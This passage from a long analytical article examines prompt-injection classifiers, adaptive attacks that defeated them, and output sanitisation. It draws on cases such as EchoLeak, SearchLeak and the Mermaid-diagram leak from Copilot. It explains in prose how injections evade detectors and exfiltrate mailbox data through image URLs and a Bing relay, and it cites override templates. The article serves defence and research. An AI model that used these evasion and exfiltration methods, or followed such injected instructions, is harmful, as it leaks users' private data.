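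TaskTracker's training data consisted of ordinary questions and tasks inserted into paragraphs, without any jailbreaks or openly malicious instructions. On a test set that included these, its AUC was above 0.99 for all six language models. It did better than the first Prompt Guard and Microsoft's Prompt Shields in its developers' tests. TaskTracker needs access to the model's activations, so a company that only rents a model through an online service cannot use it unless the provider offers it.

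A high AUC can be misleading here too. Kale and Vishwanath studied a different kind of probe, one that reads the activations once, just before an agent acts. They found that a classifier given only seven simple statistics, such as the number of messages so far and the length of the latest tool output, reached an AUC of 0.91 to 0.98 on the standard AgentDojo test. Injections there tend to arrive at predictable points and make the text longer, so a detector can score well without recognising injections.

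To expose such shortcuts, the researchers compared each attack with its "clean twin", the same moment in the same task without the injection. At the default threshold of 0.5, the standard probe flagged a median of 80% of the clean twins across six open models. It also flagged 98% of harmless notices formatted like an attack and 90% of harmless instructions to people, such as a request to bring a laptop to a workshop.

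After Kale and Vishwanath added clean twins and harmless look-alikes to the training data, these figures fell to 17%, 11% and 33% in apps the probe had trained on. Flagging a third of harmless requests to people is still a lot for a filter on business email. But a stricter threshold, which flagged 1% of normal tool outputs in the training apps, caught a median of 95% of the attacks that had fooled the agent.

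Better training data can greatly reduce the number of outputs that need a second check. In a simulation where 1% of tool outputs contained attacks, the standard probe at its default threshold sent 315,000 of every million outputs to the second check, compared with 74,000 for the retrained probe. At one second per output, the second check would take 88 hours with the standard probe and 21 hours with the retrained one. Kale and Vishwanath note that Anthropic runs injection probes on tool outputs across many of its products.

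### What Microsoft and Google document

Microsoft announced Prompt Shields in March 2024 as a preview for developers using its AI services (Zarfati, 2024, *Azure AI announces Prompt Shields for Jailbreak and Indirect prompt injection attacks*). Microsoft's current documentation distinguishes attacks typed by the user from "document attacks", which are injections in emails, files or web pages. The service can scan for document attacks in both the user's input and tool responses.

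Developers choose whether Prompt Shields blocks an attack or only annotates it. The result contains separate values for whether the service detected an attack and whether it filtered the text. A developer can therefore run the classifier in annotation mode first and count the false alarms before letting it block anything.

Microsoft recommends the same mode for troubleshooting false positives, and suggests exempting trusted sources from the scan. The exemption reduces false positives, but it is safe only if outsiders cannot get text into those sources. For example, an internal document may contain paragraphs an employee copied from an outside email. Microsoft's documentation gives no detection or false positive rates, so customers have to measure these on their own data.

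To protect its Gemini assistant, Google has built its own classifiers that detect malicious instructions in emails and files. It trained them with a catalogue of attacks, including some that outside researchers reported through its bug bounty programme. *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes how the company updates its defences when it learns of new attacks, but gives no error rates.

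### The shortage of realistic examples

All of these detectors depend on examples, but real attacks are scarce. Ravia said this shortage made emails like EchoLeak's hard to catch. Li and Liu combined 20 public datasets because they found that the makers of existing classifiers had mostly kept their training data private. The public datasets contained few injections in formats such as spreadsheets, so Li and Liu used GPT-4o-mini to write more examples in 17 formats, including email. With those added, the collection held 61,089 benign texts and 15,666 injections.

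Synthetic attacks tend to be obvious. Jacob and colleagues created many of theirs from templates, some of which tell the model to ignore its earlier instructions or falsely state that the original task is complete. But in the résumés that Zhang and colleagues studied, more than 90% of the hidden injections contained no explicit instruction. A classifier trained mainly on commands may be poor at detecting such injections.

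Harmless examples can be just as unrealistic. If all the attacks in a training set are emails and all the harmless texts are short chat questions, a classifier can separate them by recognising emails. *CAPTURE* (2025) addresses this by generating harmless prompts with trigger words for particular subjects. It trained separate detectors for Python programming, films and shares.

### Retraining after an incident

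Retraining a classifier takes time, so a provider that learns of an attack like EchoLeak may first block a recognisable part of it with a fixed rule. Google does this through a central system of policies, which Gavish describes as faster than updating a model. Such a rule catches copies of the attack, but *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) notes that attackers can get past fixed patterns by paraphrasing or substituting synonyms.

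The next step is to collect examples of attacks. Google gets reports from its own testers, automated attack tools, outside researchers and public disclosures. Staff reproduce each attack, check whether it is new and add it to a catalogue. A tool called Simula then generates variants, because a classifier cannot learn a general pattern from one email.

Adding only attacks to the training data would be a mistake. Aim Labs' email looked like a collection of workplace guides, so a classifier trained on many variants of it might start flagging every real onboarding guide. When Li and Liu added their examples in 17 formats, 435 in all, the share of attacks caught rose from 70% to 76%, but the share of harmless NotInject texts flagged rose from 25% to 36%.

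When the researchers retrained the classifier from scratch with the harmless texts built from trigger words, it flagged only 13% of NotInject and caught 77% of attacks. When they instead continued training the existing classifier with those texts, it still flagged 32%. Another published technique for reducing such shortcuts also lowered false alarms to 13%, but the classifier then caught only 66% of attacks.

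The harmless look-alikes need to match the new attack closely. Kale and Vishwanath used look-alikes in only one attack format. When they put harmless notices into two other formats, the retrained probe flagged 49% of them in familiar apps, compared with 11% in the format it had trained on. For an attack like EchoLeak, the provider would need genuine workplace guides and ordinary emails that ask the recipient to do something.

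The provider then has to reset the threshold, because a score of 0.9 from the new model may not mean the same as 0.9 from the old one. One method is to score a large sample of recent harmless documents and set the threshold so that only the permitted share score above it. For a false positive rate of 0.01%, that would be about 100 documents in a sample of 1,000,000.

A classifier's threshold should be set using normal traffic from the service where the classifier will run. Kale and Vishwanath trained a simple text classifier on some apps and tested it on others. With a threshold based on normal traffic in the new apps, it caught 87% of the attacks that had fooled the agent. The same classifier caught only 38% with a threshold carried over from the training apps.

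Before releasing the new version, the provider needs to test it for regressions, meaning older attacks it now misses or harmless texts it now flags. Google excludes part of its synthetic data from training and uses it for validation. It also simulates attacks on apps such as Gmail and Docs with the defence switched on and off, to measure the change's effect on the whole product.

If variants of the same email end up in both the training and validation sets, a good validation result shows only that the classifier recognises that email in new wording. The provider can better estimate how the classifier will handle unfamiliar attacks by keeping every variant of some attacks out of training and testing on those. Even then, nobody has revised the test attacks to evade the new version.

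## What happens when attackers adapt to a classifier

A provider's validation set contains existing attacks, but a real attacker can send an email, see that no data arrives, and try again with different wording. Researchers therefore distinguish a fixed test, which runs a stored set of attacks against a defence, from an *adaptive attack*, which somebody designs or repeatedly revises against the defence under test. A classifier can do very well in a fixed test and still fail against an adaptive attack.

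### What retrying does to a low success rate

Suppose a classifier and the model behind it together stop 99% of attempts, so each attempt succeeds with probability p = 1%. If attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If each attempt independently has a 1% chance of success, an attacker has a 10% chance of succeeding at least once in 10 attempts, 63% in 100, and 99% in 500. Email costs almost nothing to send, so anyone can make 100 attempts.

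Real attempts are not independent. The same email sent twice to the same classifier gets the same score, and small variations on an idea the classifier recognises tend to fail together, so the formula overstates the danger from such attempts. It understates the danger from an attacker who learns from each failure and so has a better chance next time.

An attack success rate therefore means little unless the reader knows how many attempts were made and what the rate is a share of. Some studies report the share of attempts that succeed, while others report the share of scenarios, teams or conversations in which the attacker eventually succeeds. In the example, the same system has a success rate of 1% per attempt and 63% per attacker.

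### Twelve defences against a persistent attacker

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. Four of the defences were injection classifiers: Protect AI's detector, Meta's Prompt Guard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor.

The team attacked these four classifiers with an automated search. One language model wrote several candidate injections, and the software tried each on an agent protected by the classifier. A second model rated from 1 to 10 how close each candidate had come to succeeding. The first model then used the earlier candidates and their ratings to write new ones. The search also had access to the classifier's verdict and confidence score. It ran on 80 scenarios from AgentDojo, with up to 800 queries per scenario.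 The attack succeeded in a scenario if any candidate made the agent carry out the attacker's task.

For comparison, the researchers ran a fixed attack, a standard AgentDojo template. With Gemini 2.5 Pro as the agent, the results were:

| Defence | Scenarios lost to the fixed attack | Scenarios lost to the search | Median queries to first success | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 13 | 74% |
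| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 30 | 39% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 46 | 39% |
| Prompt Guard | 26% | 94% | 21 | 72% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 22 | 59% |

The medians cover only scenarios in which the search succeeded. The Protect AI figures leave out some tasks because that detector wrongly flagged the targeted secret as an attack and removed it.

PIGuard resisted the attacks best, but it also cut the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 74% to 39%. Some of its resistance may come from blocking so much. Nasr and colleagues doubt whether the classifiers' small gains would survive at a false positive rate that users would accept. Prompt Guard barely affected ordinary work but stopped few of the attacks. Prompt Guard 2 prevented 81.2% of AgentDojo attacks in Meta's own test, but the conditions were different and the threshold may have been too.

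With GPT-5 Mini as the agent, the template never worked, even with no defence. The search succeeded in 75% of scenarios against the undefended model, so testing only the template could have suggested that the model needed no classifier. Adding Prompt Guard left the search's success rate at 75%, while Model Armor reduced it to 56% and PIGuard to 49%.

The paper's success rates of above 90% against most of the 12 defences include results for defences other than classifiers. Attacks succeeded in at least 95% of scenarios with Gemini 2.5 Pro against two of these, Spotlighting and repeating the user's request after the untrusted text. Against Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, fixed attacks had a reported success rate of 2%, while the search succeeded in 96% of scenarios. Attacks that used other methods succeeded in 96 to 100% of cases against three of the 12 defences, including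 two that deal only with jailbreaks.

Defences that rely on a secret did no better. DataSentinel, a detector that checks whether a model can still repeat a hidden key, had missed at most 7% of attacks in its developers' tests. Nasr and colleagues used reinforcement learning to train an attacking model against it, with 32 sessions of five attempts for each text. The trained attacker got past the detector every time by redefining the task the assistant was already doing, so the text contained no obviously separate command. Another defence, MELON, runs the agent a second time with a harmless request in place of the user's, and raises an alarm if the agent takes the same action again. An attacker who knew the design succeeded in 95% of scenarios by making the injection behave differently in the second run.

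The team also held a contest with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. Participants could watch the agent's reasoning and actions as it processed their text, but nobody told them which defences were in place. Together they beat every challenge, including all 29 scenarios that the automated search also attempted. The search won 69% of those scenarios with up to 800 queries per scenario, and the best participant who tried all 29 won 75%.

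Many of the successful injections looked like routine procedure, such as a note that an administrative step must come before the user's task. Nasr and colleagues argue that a detector could flag these only by also flagging harmless text much more often. EchoLeak exploited this difficulty.

The conditions favoured the attacker. Someone who emails an injection to a stranger's Copilot cannot see a confidence score or the model's reasoning. But attackers can buy an account with the same product and practise there, and they can download an open classifier such as Prompt Guard and read its scores directly.

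### Changing the text until the detector misses it

An open classifier can also help an attacker defeat a closed one. Hackett, Birch and colleagues (2025) tested this in *Bypassing Prompt Injection and Jailbreak Detection in LLM Guardrails* on Microsoft's Azure Prompt Shield and five open detectors. They altered 476 known injections and 78 jailbreaks in two ways.

In the first kind of attack, software changed the characters, for example by inserting invisible ones or swapping letters for look-alikes. People and language models can often still read such text, but a small classifier may not recognise it. The researchers tried 12 of these techniques, each of which produced one altered version of a text. In the second kind, software ranked the words by their influence on the classifier's decision, then replaced or misspelled the most influential ones until the decision changed. The researchers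 assumed no limit on the number of queries.

These are the shares of injections that each detector missed. The last two columns are averages over all techniques of each type:

| Detector | Original text | Changed characters | Changed words |
|---|---|---|---|
| Azure Prompt Shield | 41% | 72% | 63% |
| Protect AI v1 | 62% | 77% | 95% |
| Protect AI v2 | 16% | 20% | 68% |
| First Prompt Guard | 0.2% | 70% | 3% |
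| Vijil | 1% | 88% | 15% |

The sixth detector, Nvidia's NeMo Guard, looks only for jailbreaks. It missed 13% of the original attacks, 73% after changes to their characters and 65% after changes to their words.

Azure Prompt Shield missed 41% of the injections before anyone had altered them (first column), so the alterations account for less than half of the 72%. The first Prompt Guard seems to resist changes of wording, but in Li and Liu's test it also flagged 99% of harmless texts containing trigger words, and a detector that flags nearly everything is hard to evade.

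An average also understates what an attacker can do, because an attacker can try every technique and keep the best. One technique, which hides the text in invisible characters, evaded every detector every time. A provider could block it by removing those characters before the classifier reads the text, but there is no such simple fix for attacks that change the wording.

Azure Prompt Shield returns a verdict but no score, which makes it harder for an attacker to tell which words affect the result. Hackett and colleagues instead ranked the words with Protect AI's open detector, then sent the altered texts to Microsoft's. Across the eight word-changing methods, the average share of injections that got through rose from 64% to 70%. The gain is modest, but it means an attacker can usefully rank words without sending Microsoft anything.

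In this study, an attack counted as a success if the detector classified the text as harmless, but the altered injection may no longer work on the assistant. The researchers checked whether their altered prompts still worked, but say this needs more rigorous measurement. They began telling the vendors about the techniques in February 2024 and published in April 2025.

### A contest with the whole chain in place

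An injection must fool the detector, reach the model and make it act. *LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) measured these steps together in a public contest organised largely by Microsoft researchers. Participants wrote emails to a simulated assistant and tried to make it send an email to an address they specified. At the hardest level, the assistant's email also had to contain a profit forecast from another message in the mailbox, much like the date in Ana's case.

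Participants knew which defences they faced and how they worked, but not the exact name of the email tool or the assistant's instructions. After every attempt they learned which steps had succeeded, and there was no penalty for failing. The defences were Microsoft's Prompt Shield, the activation-based detector TaskTracker, a language model as judge, Spotlighting, and a combination of all four. The organisers set the detectors to flag fewer than 5% of harmless texts.

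The first phase ran from December 2024 to February 2025 and drew 370,724 submissions. About 3,000 of them, less than 1%, passed every stage. To measure what the detectors had prevented, the organisers also ran the assistant on flagged emails and found that 21,400 of them would have achieved the attacker's goal. The detectors therefore caught almost nine in ten of the emails that would otherwise have worked.

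Flagged emails were also more likely to control the assistant. About 19% of them made it call the email tool, compared with 4% of undetected emails. Wording subtle enough to pass a detector is often too subtle to steer the model, so an attacker has to find wording that does both.

At the hardest level, with GPT-4o-mini as the assistant, 60% of the teams that tried to beat Prompt Shield eventually succeeded. The share was 44% for TaskTracker, 32% for the judge and 17% for all defences combined, though fewer than 1% of individual submissions in the contest succeeded.

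Abdelnabi and colleagues also counted how many failures came before each successful team's first win. The average across all levels was 89 failed submissions for Prompt Shield, 159 for TaskTracker and 506 for the judge. If attempts were independent, 89 failures before a success would correspond to a success rate of about 1.1% per attempt, close to the example at the start of this section. The counts varied widely between teams, and the averages exclude teams that never succeeded.

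After the contest, the researchers ran the detectors on all the emails that had made the assistant call the tool. Prompt Shield caught 60% of those from the first phase, and an updated version caught 68% of the same emails. The updated version caught only 49% of those from the second phase, in March and April 2025, when participants were writing against it. A blocklist also barred close copies of earlier attacks in that phase, which pushed participants towards new ideas. These detection rates are the closest thing to a public error rate for Prompt Shield, and they show how quickly a gain from retraining can disappear.

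The collected emails also work on newer models. When sent once, unrevised, they succeeded 47% of the time against GPT-5 mini and 23% against GPT-5. The researchers also had GPT-5.4 write 500 new attacks from a list of techniques drawn from the contest. Of these attacks, 90 worked on GPT-5.4-mini and 10 on GPT-5.2, again with one attempt each.

### Google's tests on Gemini

Google DeepMind tested the same defences against fixed and adaptive attacks and published both results in *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025). The attacker plants text in a calendar invitation to try to make Gemini leak the user's passport number. Three automated methods search for effective text, using from a few hundred to more than 100,000 queries. DeepMind then tests the best text, unchanged, in 500 conversations that were not used in the search. The success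 rate is the share of those conversations in which Gemini leaks the number.

For the fixed test, the researchers developed the texts against an undefended Gemini 2.0 and then switched on each defence. For the adaptive test, they kept the defence on during the search. The table gives the highest rate that any of the three methods achieved against the four defences that try to detect an attack:

| Detection method | Fixed | Adaptive |
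|---|---|---|
| Filter for unnatural-looking text | 99.8% | 75.0% |
| Gemini judges its own response | 44.2% | 66.2% |
| Second model reads the retrieved text and the response | 68.2% | 14.8% |
| Second model reads the user's request and the response | 0.4% | 3.0% |

Two of these defences did better against the adaptive attack than against the fixed text, even though an adaptive attacker could always reuse that text. Shi and colleagues suspect that the search for a stronger attack failed because the defences gave it poor feedback. Since a failed adaptive attack shows only that one particular search failed, the higher of the two attack success rates is the one to plan for.

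The last defence withstood every attack. It uses a second model to check whether the response makes sense given the user's request. That model never reads the attacker's text, so an attacker has no direct way to manipulate it. In ordinary use, however, the right actions may depend on text the second model cannot see, as when Ana asks her assistant to deal with whatever her colleague's email says. The defence above it in the table does read the retrieved text, but in an earlier test with Gemini 1.5 it raised false alarms on 31 to 82% of harmless summaries of spam emails, depending on the model.

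Google also trained Gemini 2.5 on a large set of successful attacks. A set of 1,799 prompts developed against Gemini 2.0 succeeded 92% of the time on that model and 18% of the time on the new one. The researchers then searched for new attacks against Gemini 2.5 itself. The best one leaked the passport number in 94.6% of conversations in the calendar scenario and 53.6% in a similar email scenario, each after 2,160 queries. They write that without this second test they would have overestimated the model's robustness. The training did help, especially against attacks made of random-looking tokens, whose success rate fell from 98.6% to zero in the calendar scenario.

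### Results for models released in 2026

Developers now publish figures for injection in their system cards, the reports that accompany new models. The tests differ too much for a ranking:

| Model | Test | Attempts allowed | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface | 1 | 17.8% without safeguards |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface | 200 | 78.6% without safeguards, 57.1% with |
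| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 200 | 0% without safeguards |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's general test | 15 | 2.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Coding, adaptive attacks | 200 per scenario | 0.41% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | OpenAI's indirect injection tests | Rate per attempt | 3.77% |

The figures for Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, come from VentureBeat and are the only ones here that compare results with and without safeguards. At 200 attempts, the attacker succeeded in about a quarter fewer cases with safeguards than without them, but still succeeded in more than half of all cases. The comparison covers Anthropic's safeguards as a whole, so it does not show how much a classifier contributed.

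If attempts were independent, a 17.8% success rate per attempt would produce at least one success in 98% of cases after 20 attempts. The measured rate was 78.6% after 200, so real attempts are far from independent. Evidently, attacks succeed right away in some scenarios and keep failing in others, however often the attacker tries.

Newer models resist attacks better. According to The Decoder, which reported the Gray Swan results, Opus 5 also resisted every attack in 129 browser scenarios. Digital Applied (2026) reports attack success rates of 0.41% for Fable 5 and 2.09% for Opus 4.8 in the same coding test. The older Opus 4.6 had a rate of zero in its own coding test, which suggests that the attacks had become stronger or the scenarios harder, so a zero applies only to the attackers tested at the time.

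A figure like 0.41% implies very different levels of robustness depending on whether it counts attempts or scenarios. If one attempt in 244 works, an attacker who makes 200 independent attempts has a 56% chance of succeeding at least once. A model that loses one scenario in 244 after 200 attempts at each is very robust. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* says that the GPT-5.6 percentages count attempts in OpenAI's test environments and do not estimate the chance of a real breach. The smaller models Terra and Luna scored 3.32% and 2.94%. Direct attacks, in which the user types the malicious instruction, worked on Sol about 0.05% of the time. Anthropic and OpenAI have both released newer models since these tests.

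### Does detection have a ceiling?

Better classifiers may be unable to close the remaining gap, because a request to a human reader can have exactly the same wording as one meant for an assistant, as with EchoLeak's email. If an honest colleague and an attacker could both have written an email, a detector given only that email cannot determine which of them did.

The total variation distance from the first section makes this precise. Let TV now measure how far the wording of malicious emails differs from the wording of ordinary ones. For any detector that reads only the text,

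true positive rate − false positive rate ≤ TV

Suppose TV is 0.5 and the provider tolerates a false positive rate of 0.1%. Then no detector can catch more than 50.1% of attacks, whatever its size or training data. As attackers learn to write more like colleagues, TV falls, and so does this limit.

The inequality holds, but nobody knows the value of TV for real email. Prompt Shield's detection rate of 60 to 68% in the email contest was below the ceiling. The language-model judge caught 99.4% of the same first-phase emails, with no false alarms on the organisers' synthetic harmless ones, so much of what Prompt Shield missed was detectable. The 99.4% is a fixed-test result and overstates how well the judge handles attackers who adapt to it, because most of those emails were not aimed at the judge. About a third of the teams that did aim at it at the hardest level got through.

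Attackers are also limited in what they can write, because the email has to make the assistant do something. In the contest, emails that escaped detection were much less likely to succeed at this. An instruction to leak data must also normally say where to send it. This narrows the attacker's options, but an address doesn't by itself reveal an attack, because customers and suppliers include addresses in their emails too.

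The ceiling applies only to detectors that examine nothing but the text. Abdelnabi and colleagues recommend that future detectors check whom an instruction addresses, which actions fit the current task, and whether the user asked for the proposed action. An email asking for the profit forecast may be ordinary, but it is unusual for an assistant to send the forecast to an outsider when its user asked for a summary. Google's most successful defence used this kind of information. A mail filter that scans messages on arrival cannot use it, because the user has not yet asked for anything. And when the user makes a broad request, such as answering all of today's emails, an attacker's request may fit the task as well as a customer's.

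So the argument is sound for filters that judge an email by its wording, but much weaker for checks that compare an action with a specific request. It also applies only to the attacks that look most like ordinary mail, which most attackers may never write well enough to produce.

### What a beatable classifier is still good for

Nasr and colleagues defeated all four classifiers but still call them useful for blocking unsophisticated and opportunistic attacks. PIGuard blocked every attack that used the fixed template, and an attacker who copies a known injection from the internet is effectively using a fixed attack too.

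Classifiers also force attackers to make more attempts, which is a bigger obstacle for people than for automated attacks. In the automated search, they raised the median number of queries from 13 to between 21 and 46. The extra queries add little to the cost of an automated attack, since Google's researchers spent less than $10 developing a highly successful text against the undefended Gemini 2.0 Flash. For people writing emails by hand, going from 89 failures to 506 means several more days of work, and some will give up.

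Mass campaigns are easier to stop than single attacks because they send much the same text to thousands of mailboxes. A classifier that recognises the text in one mailbox will recognise it in nearly all of them, and if it misses the text, the provider needs only one victim's report to block the remaining copies. An attacker can avoid this by writing a different email for every target, but that loses most of the efficiency of a mass attack unless a language model does the writing.

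Retrying also makes an attacker easier to detect, because failed attempts leave traces. If a classifier flags each attempt independently with probability 60%, five attempts trigger at least one alert with probability 99%. A single alert is weak evidence, because a large mail service produces many false alarms. Dozens of alerts from one sender, or about one recipient, are much stronger evidence, and the provider can respond by blocking the sender or slowing down further attempts. The studies gave attackers hundreds or thousands of attempts without any such response, so they probably overstate what an attacker could do against a closely monitored service.

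This advantage disappears if the attacker practises elsewhere. Aim Labs spent about three months studying Copilot before it reported EchoLeak, and a criminal group could do the same using its own account. The victim's company would then receive one finished email, and its security staff would have no earlier failed attempts to notice. The provider might still see the practice attempts if it checks paying customers' accounts for them as carefully as it checks incoming mail.

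## Removing dangerous links and images from answers

If a classifier fails to flag the newsletter about party cakes, the model may end its answer with an image whose address contains the date of Ana's party. Output sanitisation can remove the image before Ana's browser requests it, no matter how the newsletter was worded.

### The steps of a sanitiser

A sanitiser first *parses* the answer, or works out its structure. Ana's answer is parsed into a list of tasks followed by an image. The sanitiser then collects every element that contains a link or can make a browser send a request. Besides images, these include videos, embedded pages and style rules that load a background picture. Listing them all is hard, so a well-designed sanitiser keeps only elements on a permitted list and deletes the rest.

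Next, the sanitiser checks where each remaining address leads. Socket's *markdown-to-markdown-sanitizer* describes a free sanitiser that the web company Vercel wrote for AI answers. Developers give it one allow-list for links and another for images, and it checks every address against the relevant list. An address such as `/docs/guide` doesn't include a site, so developers also have to specify which site it belongs to.

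When an address fails, the sanitiser can remove the element, show it as plain text or ask the user. Vercel's sanitiser keeps the text of a forbidden link but removes its destination. Streamdown, a free program that displays AI answers as they arrive, shows "[blocked]" instead, according to its manual page *Security*. If the address appeared as plain text, Ana could judge it for herself, but the date would still leak if she pasted the address into her browser.

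Asking the user for permission works only if the software waits for the answer before requesting the image. PromptArmor tested Notion AI, the assistant in the note-taking app Notion, with a résumé that contained a hidden injection. The assistant added an image to the user's hiring tracker and put the tracker's text in the image's URL. Notion asked whether the user trusted the outside site. But as hapticpaper (2026) explains, Notion had already saved the edit and the browser had already requested the image, so the data leaked even if the user refused. PromptArmor reported the flaw as unpatched.

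In 2024, Google's Colab, a service for running code in a browser, showed a confirmation page before opening a link from an answer. Johann Rehberger reported on his blog, Embrace The Red, that links to Google's own sites skipped this page. Those sites included Apps Script, where outsiders can publish small programs that receive data.

A sanitiser can also fail because nobody configured it. Streamdown removes dangerous HTML by default but permits links and images from every site, so a developer who changes nothing gets no protection from an image like the one in Ana's answer. TYPO3's *Rendering LLM Markdown server-side safely*, a guide for developers who use that website software, warns that a popular Markdown converter lets raw HTML through by default. If the converter crashes on a strange answer, the guide recommends displaying the whole answer as plain text and never passing the unchecked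 original to the browser.

### Two meanings of "after rendering"

Security guides often recommend sanitising an answer after rendering it, but developers use "rendering" for two different steps. First, a program called a renderer converts the answer's Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages. The browser then turns the HTML into a visible page. The advice is good only if "rendering" means the first step.

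The right time to sanitise is between these two steps, when the HTML shows exactly which links and images the page will contain but the browser has not yet requested anything. If the sanitiser runs after the browser has the page, it can remove the cake image from Ana's screen, but the browser will already have sent the date to the attacker's server.

Sanitising before the first step is too early, because the software then has to guess what the renderer will make of the Markdown.

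### When the filter and the renderer disagree

Here is a harmless Markdown link, without the `https://` that a real address would start with:

```
[Cake menu](cakes.example/menu)
```

A simple filter might search the answer for this pattern: words in square brackets, followed immediately by an address in parentheses. It would find the link and remove it. The same link in the reference form, which Copilot's link redaction missed in EchoLeak, looks like this:

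```
[Cake menu][1]

[1]: cakes.example/menu
```

This text has no parentheses, so the filter finds nothing. The renderer nevertheless converts both versions into the same HTML:

```
<a href="cakes.example/menu">Cake menu</a>
```

A provider could add a second pattern for the reference form, but Markdown has other link forms, such as an address in angle brackets, and many renderers add their own. A filter that checks the HTML needs only one rule for links, because the renderer has already turned both forms into `<a>` elements.

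Markdown parsers differ substantially, so text that is harmless in one may become a link in another, according to the documentation for Vercel's sanitiser. The sanitiser converts Markdown into safer Markdown, which its developers describe as generally less secure than cleaning the final HTML. They recommend it only when somebody else's software, such as GitHub's, will display the answer. A provider that displays answers in its own app controls the renderer and can check the HTML it produces.

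Vercel's sanitiser converts the Markdown to HTML, cleans the HTML and converts it back. It then replaces every character in the text that could have a special meaning in Markdown with a code, because the more common method, putting a backslash before each such character, works differently in different parsers. The result is hard for people to read but leaves little room for renderers to interpret it differently. The developers test the sanitiser with 555 attempted bypasses, using five renderers, but offer no security guarantee.

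0DIN, an AI security group, describes how an attacker can exploit such differences without knowing which renderer an app uses. Its demonstration against Google's coding tool Antigravity used injected instructions to output the same image in five formats, only one of which had to render for the attack to work.

An HTML sanitiser often returns the cleaned page as text, which the browser then parses again. The web.dev article *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* warns that the second parse can give a different result from the first, which can create vulnerabilities. It describes a sanitiser built into the browser, designed so that the page needs parsing only once.

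### Raw HTML and diagrams

Most Markdown renderers also accept HTML, so a model can write an image as an HTML tag, which a filter that looks only for Markdown will miss. An answer can also contain other notations, such as Mermaid, in which the model describes a diagram of boxes and arrows as text and the app draws it. The boxes can contain links.

The researcher Adam Logue used this feature in 2025 to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. The attack began when a user asked Copilot to summarise an Excel file from the attacker. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, white text on several sheets contained instructions that gradually changed Copilot's task. According to daily.dev's summary of Logue's article, Copilot then fetched the user's recent emails and converted them into hexadecimal code, which uses only digits and the letters a to f. It then drew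 a Mermaid diagram that looked like a login button, with a link containing the coded emails. If the user clicked the button, the emails went to the attacker's server.

A Markdown parser treats a Mermaid diagram as a block of code, and the link appears only when a second program renders that code as a drawing. This may be why Copilot's link redaction didn't stop the attack, though Microsoft has not explained the failure. A sanitiser that checks answers containing diagrams has to examine the rendered drawings too.

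Logue reported the flaw on 15 August 2025. Microsoft confirmed it on 8 September and fixed it on 26 September by making the diagrams non-interactive, so users could no longer click anything in them. This is more dependable than checking each link in a diagram, and users probably lost little. Logue received no reward because Microsoft's bounty programme did not cover Microsoft 365 Copilot at the time.

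Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) compares the attack with an earlier one on Cursor, an AI code editor that also displayed Mermaid diagrams. Cursor's diagrams could load external images, so the earlier attack could leak data without the user clicking anything.

### SearchLeak: an image request that left too early

AI apps usually *stream* answers, displaying the words while the model is still writing. A provider that sanitises only the finished answer may therefore do so too late. This happened in Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search, which finds emails, meetings and files. *SearchLeak* (2026), by the security company Varonis, describes an attack that combined this late sanitisation with two other flaws.

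The attack began with a link to Microsoft's own site. The link had a parameter meant for search terms, but Copilot treated its text as a request from the user and followed any instructions in it. SearchLeak was not strictly an indirect prompt injection, because the instructions were in the link and not in an email or document that Copilot retrieved. Varonis had used the same technique in an earlier attack on the consumer version of Copilot and was surprised that it also worked on the enterprise version.

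When the victim clicked the link, Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and took the title of an email. The instructions told it to put that title in the address of an image, using an HTML tag. Microsoft's defence against HTML in answers was to wrap the output in a code block, which makes a browser display a tag as text instead of acting on it. But Copilot added the code block only after it finished generating the answer, so the browser treated the tag as a real image and requested it while the answer was still streaming.

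Copilot's Content Security Policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's own server, but it permitted images from Bing. Bing's service for finding similar pictures takes a picture's address as a parameter, and Bing's servers fetch the picture from that address, so the attacker could use the service as a relay. The browser sent its request to Bing, Bing requested the "picture" from the attacker's server, and that server's log recorded the title of the email.

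Email titles can be valuable to an attacker because services often put login codes in them. In Varonis' example, the log recorded a six-digit security code, and such codes often remain valid for several minutes. The attack could reach anything the victim could open, including calendar entries and shared files. The victim only had to click one link, on a domain that most web filters trust. They might have noticed Copilot working for a moment and then giving an odd answer, but the data had already leaked by then.

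Microsoft published its record of the flaw, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), on 4 June as CVE-2026-42824, and Varonis published its research on 15 June. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, although it scored only 6.5 out of 10, against 9.3 for EchoLeak. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes the lower score to the need for a click. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and recorded no exploitation, but did not say which of the three weaknesses it had repaired. Varonis writes that the attack needed all three, so repairing any one would have stopped it, as with EchoLeak.

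GitLab, a site for storing and sharing program code, had the same timing problem in its assistant Duo in 2025. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* showed that a hidden comment could make Duo leak a customer's private code. Duo converted its answers to HTML while streaming them, so an image tag in an answer could send a request with the stolen code in its address, as TechRepublic's *GitLab Vulnerability ‘Highlights the Double-Edged Nature of AI Assistants’* explains. GitLab patched the flaw about a year before SearchLeak became public.

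### Checking an answer that is still arriving

Varonis recommends sanitising at the moment of rendering and not afterwards. With streaming, this is harder than it sounds, because the software has to judge an answer that is not yet complete. Take an answer of 400 tokens from a model that writes 80 tokens a second, so the whole answer takes five seconds. A provider has several options:

| Method | Delay for the user | What can go wrong |
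|---|---|---|
| Hold back the whole answer, then sanitise it | Five seconds before the first word | Nothing leaves early, but users may think the app has frozen |
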